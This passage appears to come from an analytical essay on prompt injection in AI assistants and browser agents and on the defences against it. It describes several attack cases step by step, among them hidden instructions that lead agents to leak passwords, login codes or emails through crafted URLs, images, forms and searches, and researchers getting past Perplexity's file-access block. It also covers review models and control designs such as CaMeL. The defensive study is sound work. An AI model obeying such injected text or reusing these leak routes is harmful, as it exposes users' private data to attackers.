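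The comparison warrants caution. Anthropic used it to justify making automatic review the default in August 2026 for many users of its own product, Claude Code. Anthropic doesn't report how many harmless commands the check would have blocked in the experiment, and a check that blocked everything would have scored 100%. The testers also had nothing of their own at stake, which in browser studies made people more willing to click through warnings.

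The figure may still overstate how well people review links. Anyone who read the planted command could see that it was dangerous, but an address with a few encoded characters looks much like any other. The testers were also doing programming work, and many browser agent users know less about computers.

### Why a high approval rate does not prove carelessness

In ordinary use, people approve 97% of Claude Code's permission requests. Resilient Cyber's *The Human in the Loop Illusion* quotes an earlier figure of 93%, also from Anthropic, and concludes that human approval isn't working as designed. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* attributes the problem to "approval fatigue", in which people stop paying close attention to what they approve.

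The approval rate can't establish that explanation, though it is plausible. If one request in 1,000 is malicious, a perfectly careful user would refuse that one and approve the other 999, for an approval rate of 99.9%. A user who approved 97% of requests at random would look more cautious but would let through 97% of the attacks.

Judging whether people pay attention to confirmation requests requires knowing which ones they refuse. In Anthropic's experiment, testers refused the dangerous command 13.6% of the time, while ordinary users refuse 3% of requests in general, which suggests that at least some testers read it. After 50 requests, testers refused it 5% of the time, close to the ordinary rate. The comparison is rough, because the testers and the ordinary users were different people doing different work.

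Claude Code's users reject 39% of the plans that Claude presents for approval, so they are able to say no. Plans come up less often than permission requests and describe what Claude intends to do, both of which may encourage people to read them. But a developer can also reject a safe plan because they prefer another approach, so the 39% doesn't show that people are better at detecting danger in plans.

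Stronger evidence of fatigue is that many users disable some or all of the requests, and so lose the protection those requests could offer. Anthropic reports that 62% of users have either turned off permission requests or told Claude Code to stop asking about shell commands, which can do almost anything on a computer. A quarter of interactive sessions start with permission requests turned off.

### When attacks are rare

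A second difficulty is that attacks are rare. If 100 of 100,000 requests are malicious and a user approves 95% of all requests without reading them, about 95 malicious requests get through. The user stops only about five attacks while refusing about 4,995 harmless requests, which blocks a lot of useful work.

Now suppose better software removes nine-tenths of the harmless requests and none of the malicious ones. The user sees 10,090 requests instead of 100,000, and the malicious share rises from 0.1% to about 1%. If the user still approves 95% without reading, 95 of the 100 malicious requests get through, as before. Fewer interruptions make the assistant more pleasant to use, but they improve security only if the user starts reading the remaining requests.

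Anthropic's testers refused 17% of dangerous commands early in a session. After seeing 50 or more requests, they refused about 5%, the same rate as the user in this example. If seeing fewer requests raised the user's refusal rate to 17%, 83 malicious requests would pass instead of 95, which would be an improvement, though most attacks would still succeed.

The calculation may be too pessimistic, because a user who sees a request once a month may read it far more carefully than a tester in the first minutes of a session. It could also be too optimistic, because it assumes that the software never removes a malicious request along with the harmless ones. Anthropic's automatic check would have let through 11% of the dangerous commands in the experiment.

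### Which features help

The evidence for particular features comes almost entirely from browser warnings, app installations and programming tools, and it differs a good deal in strength.

| Feature | Evidence that it helps | Main doubt |
|---|---|---|
| Safe choice made prominent | Chrome's redesign nearly doubled the share of users who turned back in a field experiment | People complied without understanding the danger |
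| Fewer requests | Repetition reduced the share who noticed a change to a third. Claude Code testers refused fewer dangerous commands late in a session | Even early in a session, testers missed most of them |
| Changing appearance | Students rejected 76% of risky apps after three weeks, against 55% with a fixed design | The study lasted only three weeks |
| Delay or extra step | Small hurdles improved people's decisions about installing software | Extra clicks often made little difference in browsers |
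| Specific content | Chrome users responded differently to different SSL errors | Chrome's new text hardly changed behaviour by itself |

Making the safe choice prominent has the strongest evidence, since Felt and colleagues compared designs on real users and saw a similar gain after release. A link dialog could easily do this by making "Find another source" the main button, but that would also steer users away from harmless links to documents they need.

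Studies disagree on whether delays and extra steps help. Bravo-Lillo and colleagues tested dialogs that briefly blocked the risky choice and drew attention to the important text, and Felt and colleagues credit small obstacles like these with improving decisions. But Akhawe and Felt found that people clicked through Chrome's malware warning at a higher rate than Firefox's, even though Chrome's took two clicks to bypass and Firefox's took one. In Firefox's SSL warning, 84% of people who made the first two clicks also made the third. People may decide once and then click as often as necessary. A delay that makes them look at the address again could help more than another button, but only if they understand the address.

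Informed consent depends most on specific content, and the evidence that such content helps is weak. Chrome's new text did little by itself, but it gave only general examples of what an attacker might steal, such as passwords and credit cards, and named nothing belonging to the reader. Felt and colleagues suggest testing warnings that show the user's own details, as a dialog naming Ana's email address would. That dialog is a well-reasoned recommendation, but it has not been tested. Similarly, narrow permissions received good ratings in *Options, Not Clicks*, but those ratings don't show that people will refuse a harmful request.

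None of these studies tested a dialog about opening a link in an AI assistant, and it is unclear whether anyone has published such a test. OpenAI could run one with the dialog it already uses. It would need to count how many people click "open", but also mix links containing invented private data with ordinary ones and compare how often people refuse each kind. If users refused both kinds equally often, they would have learned to distrust the dialog but not to recognise links that leak data.

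## Which designs limit the damage without asking the user?

Developers can build limits into an assistant that work whether or not the user reads a dialog. Microsoft (2025) calls a defence probabilistic if it makes an attack less likely to succeed, as training and filters do, and deterministic if it guarantees that a particular attack will fail. For example, if a chat page can't load outside images, injected text can't leak data through them, even if the model follows the injected instructions. The guarantee covers only that route, so its value depends on what other ways the data could leak.

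### Limits on what the answer displays

Bing Chat received one of the earliest limits of this kind. In April 2023 Rehberger told Microsoft that a comment or advert on a web page could take over the chat. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* describes his demonstration, in which the injected text took effect after two turns of conversation and made Bing Chat write an image address containing an encoded summary of the page and the chat, including any passwords on the page.

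Microsoft told Rehberger on 15 June that it had fixed the problem, although a later post on Embrace The Red dates the fix to May. His attacks stopped working, at least partly because of a new content security policy, an allowlist that the browser enforces and the model can't override. He found that the policy permitted images from four domains, all belonging to Bing, which Bing Chat needed for tasks such as displaying pictures it had created. Users lost little except images from other sites. Kokatsu's *Piloting Edge Copilot* describes a later policy for the Edge sidebar that also restricts connections, embedded pages, style sheets and media.

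Such a policy fails if a permitted service accepts data from strangers, as Bing's image search did in SearchLeak. Willison reports a similar flaw in the email app Superhuman. Its policy allowed images from `docs.google.com`, which also hosts Google Forms, and a form on that domain stores data contained in the address used to open it. When a user asked for a summary of recent mail, one hostile email made the assistant submit the contents of dozens of other emails to an attacker's form. Superhuman has fixed the flaw.

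Google has a stricter rule for Gemini. According to Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025), Gemini doesn't display any images from outside addresses, so EchoLeak's method would not work on it. But the security company Checkmarx says it found leaks through Markdown in both Gemini and Microsoft's Copilot Chat, including through image requests. If so, Google's rule may not have covered every place where Gemini displays an answer.

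A provider that wants to keep images can load them through its own server. This would have made the tracking image in ChatGPhish much less informative. But it doesn't protect private data in an image's address, because the server passes the address on, as the Teams service did in EchoLeak. To prevent theft, the server would also have to reject addresses that the model could have altered, for example by applying the public-index check.

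Links are harder to give up than images. Google checks the links in Gemini's answers against Safe Browsing, its service for detecting dangerous sites, and replaces suspicious ones with the words "suspicious link removed". This check may miss new phishing sites that don't yet look suspicious. Deactivating every link taken from the page would make those unclickable too. Users would lose little in a summary of one page, since they can still open the page and use its links there, but they would lose a lot with an assistant that searches the web, because they need links to check its sources.

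Labelling a link with its source would keep the link usable. The software could compare each address in the answer with those on the page and mark exact matches as "link from this page". In ChatGPhish, that would have shown the user that the account alert's link came from a README and not from OpenAI. An address that appears neither on the page nor in any search result is more suspicious, because the model may have composed it from private data. The studies of browser warnings give reason to doubt that most people would act on a small label, but the software could use the same comparison to deactivate links found in neither place automatically.

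Showing the full URL helps a reader notice the wrong domain, but it doesn't help them decode Ana's email address. Embrace The Red describes how Google's programming notebook, Colab, sends clicks through a Google URL that can show a confirmation page before the user leaves. This makes the destination more visible but still leaves the decision to the user.

These rules don't cover requests that never appear on the screen. Tenable noticed that Google had restricted images and links in Gemini's answers, and looked for a tool that could send data instead (Tenable's *The Trifecta*). It found Gemini's browsing tool. Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool* describes how injected text made the tool open an address containing the user's saved details and location, without asking the user to confirm. Google has since changed the tool to prevent this.

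### Limits on what the assistant can reach

If the assistant has no private data, a successful injection cannot steal any. Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* examines this approach by dividing a browser agent's surroundings into four trust zones: the chat, the outside servers that run the model, each website the user visits, and the wider internet. Attacks work by moving data between zones in ways the user did not intend.

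| Trail of Bits' name | What moves | Example from its tests |
|---|---|---|
| INJECTION | Untrusted text enters the chat | The agent says Yuri Gagarin was the first man on the Moon |
| CTX_IN | Private data from a website enters the chat | The agent reads a page in the user's logged-in account |
| REV_CTX_IN | Data from the chat changes the user's browser or accounts | The agent logs the user in to an account the attacker controls |
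| CTX_OUT | Data from the chat leaves in a request | The agent opens an address containing the user's name |

An injection alone can only spread false information. With CTX_OUT, it can also leak the conversation, and with both CTX_OUT and CTX_IN, it can leak data from the user's accounts. Injection, CTX_OUT and CTX_IN are the same as Willison's three conditions for data theft. REV_CTX_IN adds a danger his conditions don't cover, because a user who doesn't notice that they are in the attacker's account may type private information into it.

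Trail of Bits tested several browsers but doesn't name them, because their makers declined to coordinate the disclosure. It also gives no success rates. The tests show which attacks are possible, but not which products are still vulnerable to them.

Its simplest remedy is to isolate the agent's tools in a separate browser that has none of the user's cookies, history or stored data. With this isolation, the assistant could not have stolen the password in the Reddit attack on Comet, because it would not have been logged in to Gmail. But it also couldn't answer the user's email or fill their shopping basket. Users could log in again inside the separate browser for a particular task, but this is inconvenient and restores some of the risk.

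Logged-out browsing also does not protect private data already in the conversation or in the assistant's memory, where Paul's attack on Claude found the user's details. To handle hostile pages safely, a summariser would have to work without that memory too. Microsoft recommends the less drastic step of giving an agent each privilege only when it needs it and removing it after use. Organisations can also label sensitive files so that Microsoft 365 Copilot will not summarise them.

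Another option is to let an agent use private data but restrict which sites it can combine. Trail of Bits proposes extending the browser's same-origin policy to agents by keeping a list of every site and file whose content has entered the chat:

- If the list is empty, the agent can make any request.
- If it contains one site, the agent can contact only that site.
- If it contains several, the agent can't make any requests, because nobody can tell which source influenced the model.

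Web search counts as several sites, because results come from many places and an attacker can use a search to send data out. In one test, the agent searched for private data together with rare words. The attacker could then find the search in Google's Search Console, which shows site owners the searches that lead to their pages. In another test, the agent tried to open a nonexistent Wikipedia subdomain whose name contained the private data. Anyone who could watch the unencrypted lookup for that name would see the data, even though the agent had tried to contact only a permitted site.

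The rule that Trail of Bits proposes, and calls flexible, would block much of what people want from an agent. An agent that had read one shop's page could not open a second shop's page to compare prices. The rule also would not have stopped the attack that used Paul's site. That site would have been the only entry on the list, so Claude could have kept following its links and spelling out the user's name. To stop that attack, the software would have to count the user's own memories and messages as a source too.

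Sites that carry messages between users are another problem, because an agent can leak data through them without contacting a second site. Trail of Bits sent an Instagram user a direct message containing instructions. When the user asked for a summary, the agent collected contact names or parts of other messages, which it could send back to the attacker through Instagram's own chat.

Chrome lets its agent, Gemini, combine sites but tries to keep out unrelated ones. Parker describes a design with two sets of sites for each session. Gemini can only read sites in the "read-only" set, but can also click and type on those in the "read-writable" set. For a shopping task, a recipe site could go in the first set and a supermarket in the second. Chrome can withhold content from all other sites, including adverts embedded in a permitted page. The component that chooses the sites doesn't see untrusted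 page text, so injected text can't reach it directly.

A second model, the User Alignment Critic, reviews each action the main model proposes. It receives a description of the action but not the web page, and rejects the action if it doesn't serve the user's goal. After repeated rejections, the main model can hand the task back to the user.

These controls should stop an agent that was asked to summarise a Reddit post from opening Gmail. They would be less effective when a task involves both sites. If a user asks for a pair of boots and an injection changes which seller the agent picks, adding the boots to the basket still looks like part of the task. The critic's limited view protects it from hostile text but also gives it less evidence that something is wrong.

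Google's first version was also simpler than the full design. It tracked only the read-writable set, because the company wanted to see how often the limits interfered with ordinary tasks. Google tests the system with automatically generated hostile sites and offers outside researchers up to $20,000 for breaking its security boundaries. The design's placement of the limits is convincing, but Parker gives no success rates to show how well they hold.

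### Fixed rules for what an agent can do

A developer can forbid especially dangerous actions outright. Perplexity did this after researchers at the security company Zenity found a way to steal files from a Comet user's computer. Zenity announced the wider group of attacks, which it calls PleaseFix, on 3 March 2026 (Zenity, 2026).

Zenity Labs' *PerplexedBrowser* explains how the theft worked. The attacker sent a calendar invitation to what looked like an ordinary job interview, with instructions far below the visible text. When the user asked Comet to accept the meeting, the agent followed the instructions to an outside site. More instructions there, written in Hebrew, presented a search of the user's files as a treasure hunt. The agent opened a file of passwords, put its contents into a web address and opened that address. In one version of the attack, Comet warned the user only after the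 data had left, and in another it gave no warning.

Perplexity responded by blocking the agent from opening local files. Zenity Labs' *Perplexity Comet* describes checks marked "Hard Boundary" in the browser extension that carries out the model's commands. The checks are ordinary code, so manipulating the model does not bypass them. Users lose little, since they can still open local files themselves.

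The rule still took more than one attempt to get right:

| Date | Event |
|---|---|
| 22 October 2025 | Zenity reports the flaw |
| 23 January 2026 | Perplexity releases the block |
| 27 January | Zenity gets past it with a browser prefix for viewing a page's source code |
| 11 February | Perplexity releases a second fix |
| 13 February | Zenity confirms that the fix works |

Zenity's *PleaseFix Vulnerabilities* reports another bypass, which got past the filter by adding an extra ending to the file's address. Zenity says it disclosed this too, but doesn't say whether Perplexity has fixed it. Both bypasses worked because the software had to recognise every way of writing a local address. Running the agent in a process with no permission to read the disk would avoid that problem, but would take more work to build.

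A rule that restricts access to files leaves other targets exposed. Zenity says an attacker could use the same calendar invitation to take over a user's 1Password account if the password manager's browser extension was unlocked. It also says it got past blocks in Gemini in Chrome and Edge that were meant to keep agents away from programs running on the user's computer. In the Gemini test, the researchers gained control of the machine through a programming tool. Zenity sells security for AI agents and is the only source for these results, though its account of the Comet fix gives Perplexity considerable credit.

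OpenAI's Lockdown Mode removes many more capabilities at once. OpenAI introduced it for organisations in February 2026 (*Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*) and began extending it to personal accounts in June. It is optional, and OpenAI says most users don't need it.

With the mode on, ChatGPT can browse only copies of pages that OpenAI has already stored. The mode disables Deep Research, agent mode, file downloads, and network access for code written in Canvas, ChatGPT's editing workspace. Answers cannot contain images. On personal accounts, the mode also blocks live access to outside services and any changes to connected apps that conflict with its protections.

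Using stored pages prevents a leak that the public-index check allows. No request reaches the attacker's server, so the attacker learns nothing from which page the agent chooses. However, users may get old search results or none, and they lose the features that make ChatGPT useful for longer tasks.

OpenAI now makes a more cautious claim for Lockdown Mode than it did at first. Privacy Guides' *ChatGPT Adds Lockdown Mode for Protection Against Prompt Injection Attacks* (2026) quotes an early description of the mode as "deterministically preventing" requests that could carry data to an attacker. OpenAI's help page, *Lockdown Mode*, now says the mode limits such requests but can't guarantee that data will never leak. The remaining risks include connected apps, unexpected combinations of features and undiscovered techniques. Willison (2026), who has criticised OpenAI's earlier defences, nevertheless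 thinks the mode "looks really good" (*OpenAI Help*).

Apps are the largest exception to Lockdown Mode in organisations, where administrators decide which ones remain available. OpenAI advises against letting an agent make changes in an app, even a trusted one, if an outsider might see the result. For example, an agent that can post to a public software project can publish a secret there without opening a web address chosen by the attacker. Lockdown Mode also does not change network access in Codex, OpenAI's programming agent.

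OpenAI doesn't list clickable links among the features the mode restricts, so a phishing link could presumably still appear in an answer. Memory also keeps working, so if an injection got ChatGPT to save an instruction during a protected chat, that instruction could take effect in a later chat where the user had turned the mode off.

### Tracking where data came from

The designs above restrict whole sites, tools or features. Microsoft's research system FIDES uses a more precise method called information-flow control, which tracks each piece of data and checks who is allowed to receive it.

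Suppose the software records a set of permitted readers for everything the assistant handles. Anna and her mail provider may read her email, and anyone may read a public page. Something made from both can go only to readers permitted for both:

`readers(address) = readers(email) ∩ readers(page)`

The symbol `∩` means "members of both sets". If injected text makes the assistant build an address from a login code in Anna's email, only Anna and her mail provider may receive that address, so the software blocks a request to `collector.example`. Encoding the login code in base64, as in CometJacking, doesn't get around the block, because the restriction still applies to the data in its new form.

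A language model mixes everything in its context window. If it has read both an email and a web page, the software can't trace which of them influenced a particular web address and must treat both as influences. After reading one private email, the assistant might be unable to open any outside site for the rest of the conversation, even to check the weather. The same problem is behind Trail of Bits' ban on requests after several sources have entered the chat, and it is why the monitor in Dongol's proof takes away the web tool once the agent has read a hostile email.

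CaMeL, a research design from Google DeepMind, limits the damage from prompt injection by separating the model that plans from the model that reads. The planning model receives the user's request but no untrusted text, and writes the steps as a short program. A second model reads the web page, but has no tools and can only return values, such as a date or a summary. Ordinary software runs the program, tracks where each value came from, and checks those values against fixed rules before each action.

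Suppose Anna asks the assistant to summarise a page and email the summary to her sister. The program reads the page, summarises it, looks up the sister's address and sends the message. Hidden text can make the summary false, but it can't add a step that searches Anna's mailbox. If Anna instead asks the assistant to send the summary to an address given on the page, the attacker can choose the recipient. The separation doesn't prevent this, so the software needs a rule about which recipients can receive which data.

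Planning before reading also makes some tasks impossible. An agent can't plan every step of "follow the installation guide on this page" without seeing the guide, and a browser agent usually has to inspect a page to find its buttons. Microsoft says only that a related set of design patterns, which it helped develop, can stop injections "in specific scenarios".

Parker names CaMeL as a partial inspiration for Chrome's critic, which is designed for general browsing. Chrome's planning model reads web pages, so the agent can respond to what it finds there, but Parker describes the model as inherently vulnerable to injection for that reason. The critic can veto an action after the planner proposes it. Safety therefore depends partly on a second model's judgement, whereas CaMeL fixes the plan before any hostile text arrives.

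Even strict tracking can miss information that an agent reveals by choosing whether to open a page. For example, if the agent opens a harmless page only when Anna's mailbox contains a message from a clinic, opening the page reveals that she has such a message.

### One summary with and without mailbox access and live links

Suppose Anna asks for a summary of a page about walking boots. Hidden text on the page instructs the assistant to say that the maker has recalled the boots, add an account alert with a link to a fake login page, and put the latest login code from her email into a link labelled "size guide".

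A connected assistant can read the user's mailbox and display live links, while a plain summariser can do neither. In this hypothetical comparison, the model obeys the hidden text in both cases, and neither product loads images or opens further pages by itself.

| What the injection attempts | Connected assistant | Plain summariser |
|---|---|---|
| False recall notice | Anna reads it | Anna reads it |
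| Fake account alert | One click opens the attacker's login page | Anna would have to copy the address into her browser |
| Theft of the login code | One click on "size guide" sends it | The assistant has no code to send |
| Theft of details from the conversation | One click can send them | They stay on the screen unless Anna copies the address |

If 10,000 people request the summary and the injection works 1% of the time, each design produces about 100 manipulated answers. If a fifth of the people who see the "size guide" link click it, the connected assistant sends about 20 login codes to the attacker. Training that prevented 90% of the injections would reduce this to about two. The plain summariser sends none in either case.

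The two restrictions also prevent different harms. Removing only mailbox access stops the assistant from revealing the login code, but the fake alert still links to a phishing page. If only the links are deactivated, the alert has nothing to click, and although the code might appear in the answer, only Anna can see it there. For this page, deactivating links therefore prevents more harm and still lets Anna ask about her email. This is true only if the assistant has no other way to send data, and a browsing tool like Gemini's would give it one.

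Neither restriction removes the false recall notice. Anna could discover it by reading the page herself, but she asked for a summary to avoid doing that.
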